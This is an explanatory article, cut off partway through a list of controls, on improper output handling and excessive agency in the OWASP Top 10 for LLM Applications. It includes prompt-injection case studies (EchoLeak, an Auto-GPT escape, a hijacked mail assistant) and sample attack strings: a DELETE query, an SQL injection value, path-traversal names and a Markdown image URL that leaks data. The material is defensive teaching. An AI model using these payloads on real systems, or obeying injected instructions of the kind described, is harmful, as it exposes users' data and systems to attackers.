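# Insecure output handling and excessive agency in the OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications

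## What is the OWASP list, and what happens after a model generates text?

The OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications ranks ten security risks in software that relies on a large language model (LLM), the kind of program behind ChatGPT, which responds to text with text. OWASP, the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, is an online community that publishes free articles, tools and documentation on software security. The OWASP Foundation, a US non-profit, runs it. OWASP's best-known publication is an older Top 10 for web applications, and Real Python's *OWASP LLM Top 10* explains that the LLM list does the same job for software that uses a language model. The LLM list first came out in July 2023, after the chatbots of late 2022 led businesses to rush language models into their products. The current version dates from August 2026.

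Two of the ten entries concern what an application does with text the model has produced. In the first, the application passes that text unchecked to a browser, a database or some other program. OWASP called this Insecure Output Handling in 2023 and has called it Improper Output Handling since the 2025 edition; "output handling" here refers to both. The second, excessive agency, is a design flaw in which the application gives the model more power to act than its task requires, so a bad output can lead to a damaging action.

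### Who uses the list, and for what

Version 1.1 of the list is mainly for the developers, data scientists and security experts who design and build these applications (OWASP, 2023). The web page for the newest edition adds architects and chief information security officers (OWASP, 2026). When version 1.0 appeared, Paganini (2023) reported that the project aimed to educate developers, managers and organisations about the risks of deploying these models. In the announcement of the 2023 list's successor, project founder Steve Wilson praised the 2023 list for "raising awareness and building a foundation for secure LLM usage" (OWASP, 2024).

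The Top 10 is an awareness document, not a certification standard. A typical entry describes a risk, gives a few examples and attack scenarios, and suggests mitigations, but it does not set requirements that a tester could mark as passed or failed. For those, version 1.1 refers developers to OWASP's Application Security Verification Standard, which has detailed guidance on checking input and encoding output. Security teams also use the Top 10 to define controls and to document AI risk for auditors and boards, according to *What is the OWASP Top 10 for LLM and Agentic AI* by the security vendor CyberSaint. The order of the entries therefore has some practical effect, since a team with limited time may well start at the top.

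Security companies also help to pay for the project. OWASP opened a sponsorship programme in November 2024, and the first sponsors included Palo Alto Networks, Lakera, HiddenLayer and Snyk, which sell protection against such risks. OWASP describes the project as industry-neutral and gives the list away, but the sponsors' endorsements in its press releases come from interested parties.

### One request, step by step

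Suppose an assistant summarises a person's email, an example OWASP uses to illustrate excessive agency. The user asks, "Which of this morning's messages do I need to answer?"

The application first takes the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), adds the user's question, and fetches the new messages from the mailbox (retrieval). It then joins everything into one long input and sends it to the model.

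The model produces more text, which the application holds as a string of characters, much as if somebody had typed it into a form. Nothing has yet happened in the outside world.

What comes next depends on the application's code, which can do one of three things with the string:

- It can display the text. The application puts the summary into a web page, and the user's browser renders it.
- It can pass the text to another program. To find older messages from the same sender, the application might ask the model for a database query and then run that query.
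- It can treat the text as a request to run a tool.

A tool is a function that the model can ask the application to run, such as one that sends an email. OWASP called much the same thing a "plugin" in 2023 and an "extension" in the 2025 edition. The model only produces text that names the function and supplies the arguments. The application then makes the call, using whatever account and passwords the developer has given that tool.

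Many applications repeat this loop. In an agent, the model chooses among tools and the application calls the model repeatedly, feeding the result of each step into the next. Asked once to arrange a meeting, an agent might look up two calendars, pick a free hour, write the invitation and send it.

Both entries concern what happens after a model generates text and before that text has an effect. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* covers the checking and cleaning of model outputs "before they are passed downstream to other components and systems". *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* covers what can act on the output, and divides the excess into functionality, permissions and autonomy. If the email assistant's summary goes into the web page with its code intact, that is a failure of output handling. Giving the assistant a "send message" function that summarising never requires is excessive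 agency.

Other entries on the list concern earlier stages. Tampering with training data happens before the application exists, and prompt injection enters with the text that the application gathers at the start.

### What the receiving program can do with the text

A downstream interpreter is any program that receives model output and acts on it. Examples include the browser that renders the email summary, databases, terminals, shells (programs that run typed commands) and APIs (interfaces through which programs call one another). These programs have their own languages, and text that looks like harmless prose to a person may contain something the interpreter executes.

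Web developers knew about the resulting attacks long before language models existed. Four recur throughout OWASP's entries and in vendors' guides to those entries, such as StackHawk's *Understanding and Protecting Against LLM05*.

- Cross-site scripting (XSS) means that an attacker's code runs in another person's browser. Example: a chatbot's answer contains a piece of JavaScript, the web page inserts the answer as it stands, and the reader's browser runs the script.
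- SQL injection means that text meant as data becomes part of a command in SQL, the usual language of databases. Example: an application pastes a "customer name" from the model into a query, and the name ends with an instruction to delete a table.
- Server-side request forgery (SSRF) means that an attacker gets a server to send requests on the attacker's behalf, often to internal systems that outsiders cannot reach. Example: the model's text includes the address of a company's private administration page, and the application's server fetches it.
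- Remote code execution (RCE) means that an attacker runs code of their own choosing on somebody else's machine. Example: the application hands the model's text straight to a shell, and the text includes a command that downloads and starts a program.

Least privilege, the rule that a component gets only the access its task requires, is an equally old idea. In OWASP's example, an application that recommends products to customers should have a database account that can read the products table but not access other tables or change records. The rule limits what bad model output can cause, though it does not improve the output.

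### Why the text may be under an attacker's influence

OWASP warns that whoever controls a model's input can, to some degree, control its output. An application that passes the output on without checks therefore gives its users what version 1.1 of the list calls "indirect access to additional functionality". Developers know that a stranger wrote the text they receive from a web form, but model output is easier to trust because it comes from a component they chose and configured.

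This kind of control is called prompt injection, in which text makes a model depart from its developer's intent. Direct injection comes from the person using the application, such as a customer who tells a support chatbot to forget its instructions and search the company's private records. Indirect injection comes from content that the model processes. For example, an attacker hides a line in a web page telling the model to delete the reader's emails, and the model deletes them when a user asks for a summary of the page. The application's owner usually has the most to lose from direct injection, while the victim of indirect injection is often a user who has done nothing unusual.

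Indirect injection works because the application gives the model the developer's instructions, the user's request and the contents of the emails as one sequence of text. A well-written database program sends commands and data separately, in a parameterised query, so the database never reads a customer's name as a command. By contrast, OWASP says in version 1.1 that LLMs "do not segregate instructions and external data from each other". It recommends that developers mark the parts, for instance with a format that labels each stretch of text by its source, but the labels are more input to the model, and nothing outside the model enforces them. A well-trained model may nearly always respect them, but OWASP concluded in 2023 that the model itself offers "no fool-proof prevention".

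Greshake, Endres and colleagues introduced the indirect attack in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023), in which they planted instructions in material that an application was likely to fetch. They tested it on Bing's chat service, which ran on OpenAI's GPT-4, on code-completion engines, and on test applications of their own. In Microsoft's Edge browser, Bing's chat sidebar could read the page that the user was viewing, and instructions on that page affected the model even when the user could not see them. The planted text could also influence whether and how an application called other programs. They compared processing untrusted text in such an application to running untrusted code.

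Two of their observations make input filtering look unpromising. First, an attacker can encode the instructions, place them in an image, or plant a short instruction that makes the model fetch a longer one from elsewhere, so a filter has to recognise many forms of attack. Second, in their trials the attacker could sometimes just state a goal and leave the model to work out the steps. This suggests that a more capable model may also be more useful to an attacker who hijacks it.

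Their evidence consists of worked examples on systems from early 2023. These show that the attack is possible but give little indication of how often it succeeds, especially against current models. The later record of incidents is thinner than the attack's reputation would suggest. OWASP kept prompt injection in first place in its 2026 edition, which Infosecurity Magazine covered under the headline *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*. According to Cyber Security News, the reasoning is that every point where a model takes in untrusted text stays open to attack, whether or not anyone has publicly exploited it.

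OWASP recommends putting the controls outside the model. In the release announcing the 2026 edition (OWASP, 2026), Wilson urged security teams to assume that AI "will sometimes fail or be fooled" and to place enforceable limits on what it can access, decide and do. The first draft made the same point three years earlier, advising that models "should not self-police".

Such limits are useful even when there is no attacker. OWASP's definition of excessive agency covers damage from bad output whatever the cause, and version 1.1 names several causes that don't involve an attacker, such as hallucination, a badly written prompt or a poorly performing model. Even with a complete fix for prompt injection, an email assistant with an unnecessary delete function could still delete the wrong message.

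### The editions and their numbering

OWASP has published the list five times, counting a draft. The table gives the rank of every entry that concerns the stage after generation.

| Edition | Date | Output handling | Plugins and their permissions | Excessive agency |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Version 0.5 (draft) | 1 July 2023 | LLM02 | LLM06 Permission Issues; LLM10 Insecure Plugins | LLM08 |
| Version 1.0 | 1 August 2023 | LLM02 | LLM07 Insecure Plugin Design | LLM08 |
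| Version 1.1 | 16 October 2023 | LLM02 | LLM07 Insecure Plugin Design | LLM08 |
| 2025 edition | 17 November 2024 | LLM05 | no separate entry | LLM06 |
| 2026 edition | 3 August 2026 | LLM10 | no separate entry | LLM03 |

The July 2023 ranks come from the draft that OWASP (2023) presented as a preview, and the August ranks come from the OWASP (2023) slides for version 1.0. For 2026, SC Media's *OWASP updates top 10 security risks for LLM applications* lists the ten categories in order, and Respan's *OWASP LLM Top 10* gives their official labels. The 2026 edition is also the first for which OWASP considered a record of reported incidents alongside the contributors' vote.

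The numbers are ranks that change between versions of the list, so a label without its year can mislead. LLM06 meant Permission Issues in the July 2023 draft and Sensitive Information Disclosure a month later. In the 2025 edition it meant Excessive Agency, and in the 2026 edition it means Unbounded Consumption, the risk that an application uses up computing resources or money without limit. Similarly, LLM05 in an older guide may refer to output handling or to the supply chain. OWASP therefore includes the year in the label, as in LLM06:2025.

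## How does unchecked model output become an attack?

Output handling, which OWASP now labels LLM10:2026, concerns an attack that takes four steps:

1. An attacker gets some text in front of the model, through direct or indirect prompt injection.
2. The model responds with text of its own.
3. The application hands that text to a downstream interpreter without checking it.
4. The interpreter finds something in the text that it can execute, such as a script, a query or a command.

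If a model outputs `DELETE FROM orders`, the text is harmless in a chat window or a log file. It does damage only when the application runs it on a database through an account with permission to delete orders. The flaw is therefore in the application code that passes the text to the database, and a developer can fix it there without changing the model.

*Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (2026), which compares attacks on LLM applications with older attacks on websites, matches insecure output handling to two entries in the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), MITRE's public catalogue of software weaknesses. CWE-116 is the failure to encode output properly for the program that receives it. CWE-502 is the rebuilding of program objects from untrusted data, which can run code hidden in the data. In an ordinary web attack, the attacker writes the malicious script or SQL and sends it, whereas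 in an LLM application the attacker prompts the model to write it.

*From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (2026) traces an attacker's request through the model and into a database. The request can be in plain language with no SQL in it, which weakens the familiar defence of scanning incoming messages for code. The paper describes a chatbot whose database account could read every table and run any kind of statement. An outsider with no database account could use all of those permissions by asking in the chat.

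Unchecked model output can also cause harm without an attacker. In a scenario from StackHawk, a business analyst asks for a list of customers who have bought nothing for a year. The model writes a query that deletes the customer data, and the application runs it on the live database. The application makes the same mistake here as in an attack, so the same checks help in both cases.

The right check depends on which interpreter receives the model's output. OWASP's 2023 entry, *LLM02*, gave only shells and browsers as common examples, and the 2025 edition added SQL, file paths and email templates.

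### Browsers

In cross-site scripting through a chatbot, the browser cannot distinguish a script produced by the model from one written by the site's developers, so it runs the script with the user's login. The script can then read what the user sees and send requests in the user's name. This would be serious on a bank's website, the example in *Shifting from Injection to Interaction*.

Users who get the model to output a script in their own chat window attack only themselves, which achieves little. The attack matters when the script reaches someone else's browser. This can happen when a support agent later opens the conversation, or when the model summarises an attacker's page for another user. In one OWASP scenario, a company uses a model to write marketing emails and an attacker gets JavaScript into them. The script runs for any recipient whose email program is vulnerable, even though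 the recipients never use the application.

The basic check is output encoding, which replaces characters that have a special meaning in HTML. For example, the encoder turns `<` into `&lt;`, so the browser displays a "less than" sign instead of starting a tag.

Chatbots complicate this because they usually answer in Markdown, a light notation for bold text, lists and links, which the application converts to HTML. If the application encoded everything after the conversion, readers would see raw tags. It needs a converter that ignores any HTML the model wrote, followed by a filter that removes every tag not on a list of permitted ones, called an allow-list. Bugcrowd, a security vendor, recommends applying allow-lists before a response reaches the program that displays it. Links need a separate check because an address that starts with `javascript:` can run code when the reader clicks it, and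 HTML encoding doesn't change that prefix. The simplest rule is to allow only addresses that start with `https:`.

OWASP also recommends a strict Content Security Policy (CSP), a set of rules a website sends with its pages to limit where the browser may load scripts and other material from. If the policy forbids scripts written directly into the page, the browser won't run a script in the model's output even when the encoding step has failed. The rest of the output still can't be trusted, since a fake login form needs no script.

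### Databases: a worked example

Suppose an online shop adds a chat feature that answers questions about orders. Its database has an `orders` table with columns for the customer's number, the item and its status. Customer 17 has signed in.

In the first version of the feature, the application tells the model how the table is laid out and which customer is asking. It then asks for an SQL query and runs whatever comes back. The customer wants to know where a parcel is, and the model writes:

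```sql
SELECT item, status FROM orders WHERE customer_id = 17;
```

This works. Next, the customer claims to be a member of staff and asks to see everybody's orders. The model may refuse, but if it complies it writes:

```sql
SELECT item, status FROM orders;
```

The query is valid and the account may read the table, so the database returns every shopper's purchases. A request to clear out old cancellations might produce:

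```sql
DELETE FROM orders WHERE status = 'cancelled';
```

The developer could tell the model to write only queries about customer 17 and never to delete anything. That would make these results less likely, but the application would still run whatever query the model wrote.

OWASP advises using parameterised queries for every database operation that involves model output, but this advice is easy to misapply here. Parameterised queries protect a statement that the developer has written with placeholders for the values. In the shop's first version, the model writes the whole statement, so there is no fixed part to protect, and the database's parameterised interface would still run the `DELETE`.

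The second version stops asking the model for SQL. The developer writes one query:

```sql
SELECT item, status FROM orders WHERE customer_id = ? AND status = ?;
```

The model now only identifies which status the customer is asking about, and the application accepts one of four words: `processing`, `shipped`, `delivered` or `cancelled`. The application puts that word in the second placeholder and fills the first from the login session, which the model cannot change.

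If customer 17 now asks for everybody's orders, the worst the model can do is choose the wrong status, and the customer sees some of their own orders. If the model returns `shipped' OR 'a'='a`, a classic SQL injection that would make the condition always true, the application rejects it because it isn't one of the four words. Even without that check, the database would look for an order whose status was literally that string and find none.

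The developer also gives the feature its own database account, which can only read the `orders` table. If a later feature runs unchecked model-written SQL through the same account, a `DELETE` will fail with a permission error. But the read-only account would not have stopped the model in the first version from listing everybody's orders, because the account serves every customer and must be able to read all their rows. Some databases can prevent this with row-level rules, which limit each connection to one customer's rows.

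A fixed query can answer only questions that the developer foresaw. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre advises against running model-written SQL directly and suggests strict query builders where possible. With a query builder, the model could choose columns and filters from a permitted set while ordinary code assembled the statement. An analyst who explores sales data may need more freedom than that. The protection then has to come mostly from restricting the tool's database account, for example to reading a separate copy of data that the analyst is allowed to see in full.

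### Shells and code evaluators

A shell runs commands, and Python functions such as `exec` and `eval` run program code. When model output reaches any of these, it can harm the machine's owner and everyone whose data is stored on it.

OWASP's entry links to a 2023 case under the heading "Arbitrary Code Execution". The case involved LangChain, an open-source library that developers use to connect models to databases, search engines and other programs. To make up for the weak arithmetic of early models, its LLMMathChain component prompted the model to turn a question into a short piece of Python, then ran that code with `exec`. A user could ask for something other than a sum, and the server would run the resulting code. The flaw was publicly recorded as CVE-2023-29374 in April 2023 and affects versions up to 0.0.131. LangChain's developers later replaced `exec` with numexpr, a library meant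 to evaluate only numerical expressions, so the application no longer depended on the model to write only harmless programs.

The Isle of Man centre advises against ever piping model output into shells, `exec`, `eval` or privileged functions. There is often an easy alternative. If a user wants to resize a photo, the application can call the image program itself and take only the width from the model, after checking that it is a number. Similarly, instead of rebuilding program objects from model output (the CWE-502 weakness), the application can ask for a plain data format such as JSON, which holds values and no code, and check that the expected fields are there. That check covers only the shape of the data, so a well-formed field can still contain a hostile string, which the application must handle safely wherever it uses it next.

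Some products are built to run code that a model has written, such as assistants that analyse a spreadsheet by writing a program. It is very hard to tell in advance whether an arbitrary program is safe, so these products need a sandbox, an isolated environment where the code can do little harm. A good sandbox contains no passwords, has no access to the company's network and limits how long code can run.

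Even when model-written code runs in a sandbox, the software around the sandbox can mishandle model output. Auto-GPT, an early open-source agent, ran model-written Python in a Docker container, a common kind of sandbox, but also let the model name the file that held the code. According to the monitoring company Coralogix, instructions on an attacker's website led the model to supply a name containing a path, and the attack escaped the container. The file could overwrite one of Auto-GPT's own program files, which would then run outside the container the next time somebody started the agent. The maintainers fixed the flaw, CVE-2023-37274, in version 0.4.3.

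### File paths and web addresses

The Auto-GPT attack relied on path traversal. In a file path, `../` means "go up one folder", so a name such as `../../settings.py` refers to a file outside the folder the developer intended. Depending on what the application does with the name, an attacker may read private files or replace important ones.

Deleting every `../` from the name in a single pass is a poor check, because if the model writes `....//`, the deletion leaves `../` behind. Having the application choose the file name is safer. If the model must choose, the application can work out the complete path and confirm that it is inside the permitted folder before opening anything.

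If the model chooses which web address the application's server fetches, an attacker can use server-side request forgery to reach the company's internal machines.

An allow-list is the best check when the feature needs only a few sites. Blocking known internal addresses is weaker, because one machine can have several names and its numerical address can be written in several ways. If the feature has to read arbitrary web pages, its server can look up the numerical address behind each name and refuse anything internal. It has to repeat the check after every redirect, since a harmless-looking site can forward the request to an internal one.

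### Images that load by themselves

In the cases so far, the interpreter does something that the developer never intended. Data can also leave through a feature that is working normally. When a page contains an image from another website, the browser requests it at once, and the request includes the image's full address. Suppose a chatbot's answer contains this Markdown:

```markdown
![chart](https://example.com/chart.png?note=meeting-at-noon)
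```

The reader sees a chart or a broken-image icon, while the website's owner receives a request containing the words `meeting-at-noon`. If an attacker's hidden text has told the model to replace those words with private information from the conversation, the attacker can simply read that information in the server's log. No script runs, and the reader doesn't have to click anything. The victim is the person whose conversation or documents the model could read. OWASP's scenario of a web page summariser that sends private content to an attacker's server can work this way.

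The EchoLeak attack (CVE-2025-32711) got data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can search a user's work emails, documents and chats. According to Coralogix, a crafted email made Copilot put the user's sensitive data into a web address. The victim did not have to open the email, only ask Copilot an ordinary question later. Copilot could then retrieve the email along with relevant documents and follow the attacker's instructions. The research group Aim Labs found the flaw and published it in June 2025.

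Two existing controls failed to stop the data from reaching the attacker. Copilot removed outside links from its answers, but it missed a less common Markdown form that puts the address apart from the text that refers to it. The page's Content Security Policy let the browser load images only from certain sites, but one permitted address belonged to Microsoft Teams and would fetch an outside address on request. The user's browser therefore requested the image from a Microsoft server, which passed the request on to the attacker with the data still in it.

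Copilot runs on Microsoft's own servers, so the flaw has no version numbers, unlike LangChain's. Microsoft fixed it without customers having to install anything, and said it had not affected any of them. The case is good evidence that the route works against a major commercial product, but it was a demonstration by researchers, not a known theft.

The surest defense is not to load remote images that the model links to. If the product needs images, the application can limit them to a short list of sites, and EchoLeak is a reason to check closely what each allowed site does with a request. Ordinary links are less risky because the reader has to click them, but their addresses can also carry private data. Showing the full address before the click gives the reader some chance of noticing that data.

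### Terminals and editors

A terminal is the text window in which developers type commands and read the results. It displays most of what a program sends to it, but it treats ANSI escape sequences as instructions. Each sequence begins with an invisible control character called escape, and the terminal acts on the codes that follow. These sequences normally have useful effects, such as colouring an error message red.

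Terminal escape sequences can also mislead the user. MITRE warns that they can move the cursor, clear the screen and create fake prompts, and that in some terminals they can run arbitrary code. Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa* (2024) connected this old problem with language models, reporting that many models can produce the escape character. GBHackers reports that in a test with a small program that sent model output to a terminal, a malicious file caused flashing text and beeps, and that other sequences could hide text or copy something to the clipboard without asking. In the terminal of Visual Studio Code, a popular code editor, the output could include clickable links that might leak data. The same technique can make an approval prompt misstate what the user is approving, for instance by clearing the line that shows the real command and printing a harmless one in its place.

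To check model output before printing it, the application keeps the control characters it needs, such as line breaks, and removes the rest or replaces them with visible symbols. An application that uses coloured text can add its own colour codes afterwards.

The 2026 edition covers terminals and editors that act on these sequences, and programs that automatically fetch outside resources named in model output, according to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026). Help Net Security's *OWASP 2026 LLM Top 10* (2026) also reports that the entry's scope grew, even though it fell to tenth place. A ReversingLabs article (2026) appears to assign the same two additions to a different entry, vector and embedding weaknesses, but Invicti lists that entry's scope as unchanged.

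### Why one "sanitise" step cannot serve every interpreter

A character that is harmless in one language can be a command in another, so cleaning the model's text once, when it arrives, does not make it safe to use everywhere.

| Character | In a web page (HTML) | In SQL | In a Unix shell |
|---|---|---|---|
| `<` | starts a tag | means "less than" | reads input from a file |
| `'` | can start or end an attribute's value | starts or ends a piece of text | starts or ends a piece of literal text |
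| `&` | starts a character code such as `&lt;` | has no special role in standard SQL | runs a command in the background |
| `;` | ends a character code | ends a statement | ends a command |

Suppose an application encodes all model output for HTML as soon as it receives it. The surname O'Brien becomes `O&#39;Brien`, which a web page displays correctly. But if the application saves that version in its database, the customer's next printed letter will be addressed to "O&#39;Brien". HTML encoding also misses some dangerous output, because it doesn't change the path `../../settings.py` or the address of an internal server.

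Deleting every suspicious character is no better. It would remove apostrophes, ampersands and semicolons, which ordinary writing needs, and the text would still be unsafe if the application later sent it to an interpreter the developer had forgotten. Even one web page contains several languages. Text between two HTML tags needs different encoding from text inside a script or a web address, so OWASP recommends "context-aware" encoding.

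Validation and encoding are easy to confuse. Validation checks whether the output is what the application expected, such as a date or one of four order statuses. The application can do this early because the result doesn't depend on where the text is going. Encoding makes arbitrary text safe for one particular destination, so it belongs in the code that sends the text there. The shop's chat feature could rely mainly on validation because it needed only a single word. A chatbot that writes paragraphs depends much more on encoding because its developers can't list the acceptable answers in advance.

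OWASP recommends treating the model "as any other user", with no special trust. It also recommends logging outputs and watching for unusual patterns, which may reveal an attack that got past the other checks. However, the interpreter may well have acted on the output by the time anyone reads the log.

### Code written by assistants

The 2026 edition also appears to cover insecure code from AI programming assistants under output handling. Mittelstand Cafe's *Top 10 für LLM-Anwendungen 2026* (2026), a press release from a German company that sells checks for such code, reports that the project leaders say so in their introduction. It also describes an attack scenario from the entry in which an application compiles and ships AI-written code without human review or security tests, and attackers then exploit it. Respan gives the same account and explains that OWASP preferred widening existing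 entries to creating thin new ones.

The change is partly one of emphasis. The 2025 entry already included a scenario in which a model writing code for a software company might introduce SQL injection vulnerabilities or invent names of software packages. Attackers can register an invented name and wait for somebody to install the package. According to Mittelstand Cafe, the 2026 edition covers those packages under Supply Chain.

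Respan calls assistant-written code the same failure at a different point in the pipeline. The two are alike in that nobody checks the model's text before a machine runs it. In the shop example, though, the model's text is itself the harmful command. An assistant's program may do what the developer asked but contain a mistake, such as a missing permission check, that an outsider discovers months later. Encoding the output can't fix such a mistake. Assistant-written code should get the same checks as any other program, namely human review, automated security tests and scanning tools.

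### How often it happens

The available figures count reported flaws and don't measure how many applications are unsafe. *Demystifying LLM Supply Chain Vulnerabilities in the Wild* (2025) sorted CVEs in the software that developers use to build and run language models, and classed 98 of them, or 18.5%, as specific to language models. Of these, 24 came from failures to validate model output before a sensitive operation, including five in which prompt injection led to SQL injection. Unchecked output therefore accounted for about a quarter of the flaws specific to language models and under 5% of the total.

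Developers still seem to be making this mistake. *Four CVEs in a week, all the same shape* (ATHelper, 2026) describes four CVEs in AI and agent projects, published between 4 and 6 May 2026. In each one, the application passed model output to a privileged interpreter without checking it again, and the interpreter ran it. This blog post shows that the problem persists in separate projects, but it covers too few cases to show a trend.

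CVE counts also miss many of these flaws because they mostly cover software that other people install. A company that builds a careless chat feature for its own website will usually fix it without a public record. Insecure code from assistants is even harder to count. According to Mittelstand Cafe, OWASP noted in its 2025 list for web applications that no CVEs or CWEs specifically identify AI-generated code, so those records don't distinguish flaws written by an assistant from flaws written by a person.

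## When does an application give a model too much agency?

Encoding and validation make model output safe for the program that receives it, but they do little about a well-formed request. If a model outputs a call to the application's `send_email` function with a real address and a polite message, nothing in the call needs escaping, but the user may never have wanted to send that email. Whether the application sends it depends on what the developer has allowed the model to do.

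OWASP's 2025 entry defines excessive agency as the vulnerability that enables damaging actions in response to "unexpected, ambiguous or manipulated outputs from an LLM", regardless of why the model malfunctioned. "Agency" here means only the ability to call functions or work with other systems in response to a prompt, and doesn't imply that the model has desires.

The definition doesn't depend on the cause, so quite different mishaps count as the same flaw. Suppose a calendar assistant that can delete events empties the user's Friday. An attacker may have sent an invitation with hidden instructions, the user may have typed "clear Friday" and only meant that nobody should book anything new, or the model may have mixed up two dates. In each case the application deleted the events based only on the model's output. Showing the user the list of events before deleting them would help in all three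 cases, while a filter for malicious invitations would help only in the first.

The 2025 entry also names some less obvious routes of attack. A malicious tool can return text that steers an agent's next steps, and a compromised agent can do the same to other agents it works with.

A developer can look for excessive agency before anything goes wrong by checking which tools the model can call, what permissions the tools' accounts have, and what code runs between a request and its effect. This is easier than predicting what the model will do, especially since its behaviour may change when the supplier updates it.

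Whether a model has too much agency depends on the application's task. A delete function is normal in a file manager but excessive in a summariser. OWASP offers no scale for measuring the excess, so the developer has to decide what the application is for before judging its tools. This is simple for a program that summarises email but much harder for a general assistant, because almost any tool could be useful to someone. OWASP now also has a separate Top 10 for agentic applications, which applies when the model acts with its own tools and memory.

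### The three root causes

OWASP traces excessive agency to too much functionality, too many permissions and too much autonomy. An application can have all three problems at once. The July 2023 draft did not yet separate these causes.

**Excessive functionality** means that the model can call functions the application doesn't need. In OWASP's main example, a developer wants an agent to read documents from a repository and chooses a third-party tool that can also modify and delete them. The agent gains these abilities even though nobody decided it should have them.

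OWASP gives two other examples. In one, a team tries out a tool during development, switches to a better one and forgets to remove the first, so the model can still call it. In the other, a tool that should run one specific shell command fails to block other commands, which gives the model most of what a shell can do.

A tool has **excessive permissions** when the account it uses on another system allows more than the tool needs. A tool that only needs to read a database might log in with an account that can also insert, change and delete records. A tool for reading the current user's documents might connect through a privileged account that can open everyone's files.

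In the second case, a read-only account would not be enough, as with the shop's chat feature. If the model requests a colleague's salary letter, whether by mistake or through an attack, the document system returns it because the request comes from an account with full access. Security engineers call this the confused deputy problem, in which a program uses its wide access on behalf of someone who doesn't have that access.

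Functionality and permissions are easy to confuse because both determine what a tool can do. The tool's own code limits its functionality, while the system it connects to limits its permissions. For example, a tool might offer the model only a "read" function but log in to a database with an account that can also delete records. The model can't delete anything in normal use, but if the tool builds its queries carelessly, an SQL injection could use the account's permission to delete. If the tool instead offers a "delete" function but the account can only read, the database rejects the deletion. Restricting both means that one mistake isn't enough to cause damage.

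**Excessive autonomy** means that an application carries out high-impact actions without an independent check. OWASP's example is a tool that deletes a user's documents without asking the user to confirm. The function may be necessary and the account may have exactly the right permissions, but no person or system other than the model checks the deletion. Asking the same model whether it is sure would add little protection, because whatever misled it is probably still in its input.

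### Turning a mail summariser into a spam sender

OWASP's version 1.1 works through one attack that involves all three causes. The target is the email assistant described earlier, whose plugin can send messages as well as read them. The attack runs as follows:

1. The attacker emails the user a message containing instructions for the model.
2. The user asks for a summary of new mail, and the application puts the attacker's message into the model's input.
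3. The model follows the instructions and asks for the plugin's "send message" function, supplying the text of a spam email and its recipients.
4. The application calls the function with the access that the user granted.
5. The mail service accepts the request because that access includes sending.
6. Strangers receive spam from the user's real address.

OWASP suggests three ways to prevent this, one for each root cause. The developer can use a plugin that only reads mail. The developer can also connect to the mail service through OAuth, a standard that lets a user give an application access to an account without sharing the password. The application would request a read-only scope, which limits it to reading mail. Finally, the application can leave every message as a draft until the user reviews it and presses "send".

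| Change | Excess removed | Where the attack stops | What could undo the protection |
|---|---|---|---|
| Plugin that only reads mail | Functionality | Step 4: the application has no send function to call | A developer later adds a tool that can send |
| Read-only OAuth scope | Permissions | Step 5: the mail service refuses the request | Another tool has an account with wider access |
| User presses "send" | Autonomy | Before step 5: the message remains a draft | The user presses "send" without reading |

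A mail summariser can use both a read-only plugin and a read-only scope without losing any function, because it never needs to send mail. The read-only scope is probably the stronger restriction, because the mail service enforces it regardless of what happens inside the application. An assistant that also replies to messages can't use either restriction in the same form. It has to rely much more on the user checking each draft, so its safety depends on the user's attention.

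None of the three stops the model from following the attacker's instructions. A read-only assistant might still write a false summary or leave out an important message. If it has a tool for fetching web pages, it could also leak mail in a web address, as with the remote images described earlier. A developer therefore has to consider the tools together, since reading mail and fetching web pages may each look harmless alone.

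The 2025 entry uses the same mailbox example, but the malicious email now tells the agent to search the inbox for sensitive information and forward it to the attacker. The same three changes still work, but OWASP's fallback, a rate limit on sending, gives far less protection. If the limit were 20 messages an hour, a spammer trying to send 5,000 would get only 20 out in the first hour, leaving time to notice and stop the rest, whereas a thief might need only one message to take everything valuable in the inbox.

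### A refund limit in the prompt and in the API

Removing a function works when the application doesn't need it. OWASP's July 2023 draft, version 0.5, had a second example in which the feature needs the dangerous function. A customer service model was connected to a payment system so that it could refund customers who complained. The system prompt told the model to refund no more than one month's subscription fee, but a malicious customer used direct prompt injection to get it to refund 100 years of fees.

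At an illustrative fee of $20 a month, a refund for 100 years (1,200 months) comes to $24,000. The limit was only a sentence in the model's input, which also contained the customer's message. The payment system did not check the limit and paid the amount the application requested.

OWASP's solution was to enforce the one-month maximum in the refund API. The customer can still talk the model into requesting $24,000, but the API rejects any refund over $20.

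The developer has to write the limit carefully for that figure to hold. If the API only checks the size of each refund, the customer can ask for $20 a total of 1,200 times and receive the same $24,000. The API therefore needs to count what it has already paid. A simple version might look like this:

```python
def refund(session, amount):
    customer = session.customer_id
    limit = billing.monthly_fee(customer)
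    already_paid = billing.refunds_this_year(customer)

    if amount <= 0 or already_paid + amount > limit:
        raise PermissionError("refund limit reached")

    billing.pay_refund(customer, amount)
```

The model supplies only `amount`. The customer's identity comes from the login session, and the fee and earlier refunds come from billing records. If the model also supplied the fee, an attacker could manipulate it into reporting a fee of $24,000, and the check would pass. A real system would also have to check and pay in a single step. Otherwise, two simultaneous requests could both pass the check before the API recorded either payment.

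The draft compared such a rule to one that web developers already follow. A web page can check a form in the visitor's browser, for instance to refuse an order for minus three shirts, but the visitor controls the browser and can bypass the check, so the server has to repeat it. OWASP treated a language model like the browser, so something outside the model has to enforce the rule.

The API limit also blocks mistakes, such as a model misplacing a decimal point and requesting $200. It doesn't check whether a customer deserves a refund, so anyone who can talk the model into one may still collect $20 a year. If 10,000 customers do this, the company loses $200,000 a year. Whether that is acceptable is a business decision, but the company can calculate its maximum loss in advance, which it could not do when the limit was only in the prompt.

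Version 1.1 drops the refund example and keeps only the mailbox one. This is a pity, because the refund case better represents applications that need to do something consequential. The application needs the refund function and the user has a right to ask for a refund, so the protection has to come from a rule about the amount.

### OWASP's controls, in order

Version 1.1 lists seven controls that can prevent excessive agency, and the 2025 edition keeps them in the same order. The earlier controls apply to what the model can request, and the later ones to the system that carries out the request.

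1. Offer fewer tools. If the application has no need to fetch web pages, OWASP advises leaving that tool out altogether.
2. Give each tool fewer functions. A mailbox tool for summaries should not contain functions for deleting or sending messages.
3. Avoid open-ended functions. If an application needs to save some text in a file, a developer could let the model run a shell command, but then it could run any other command too. A tool that only writes files is safer.
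4. Limit the permissions behind each tool. The database or other receiving system should enforce the limits on the account that the tool uses, as with the product recommender that can read only one table.
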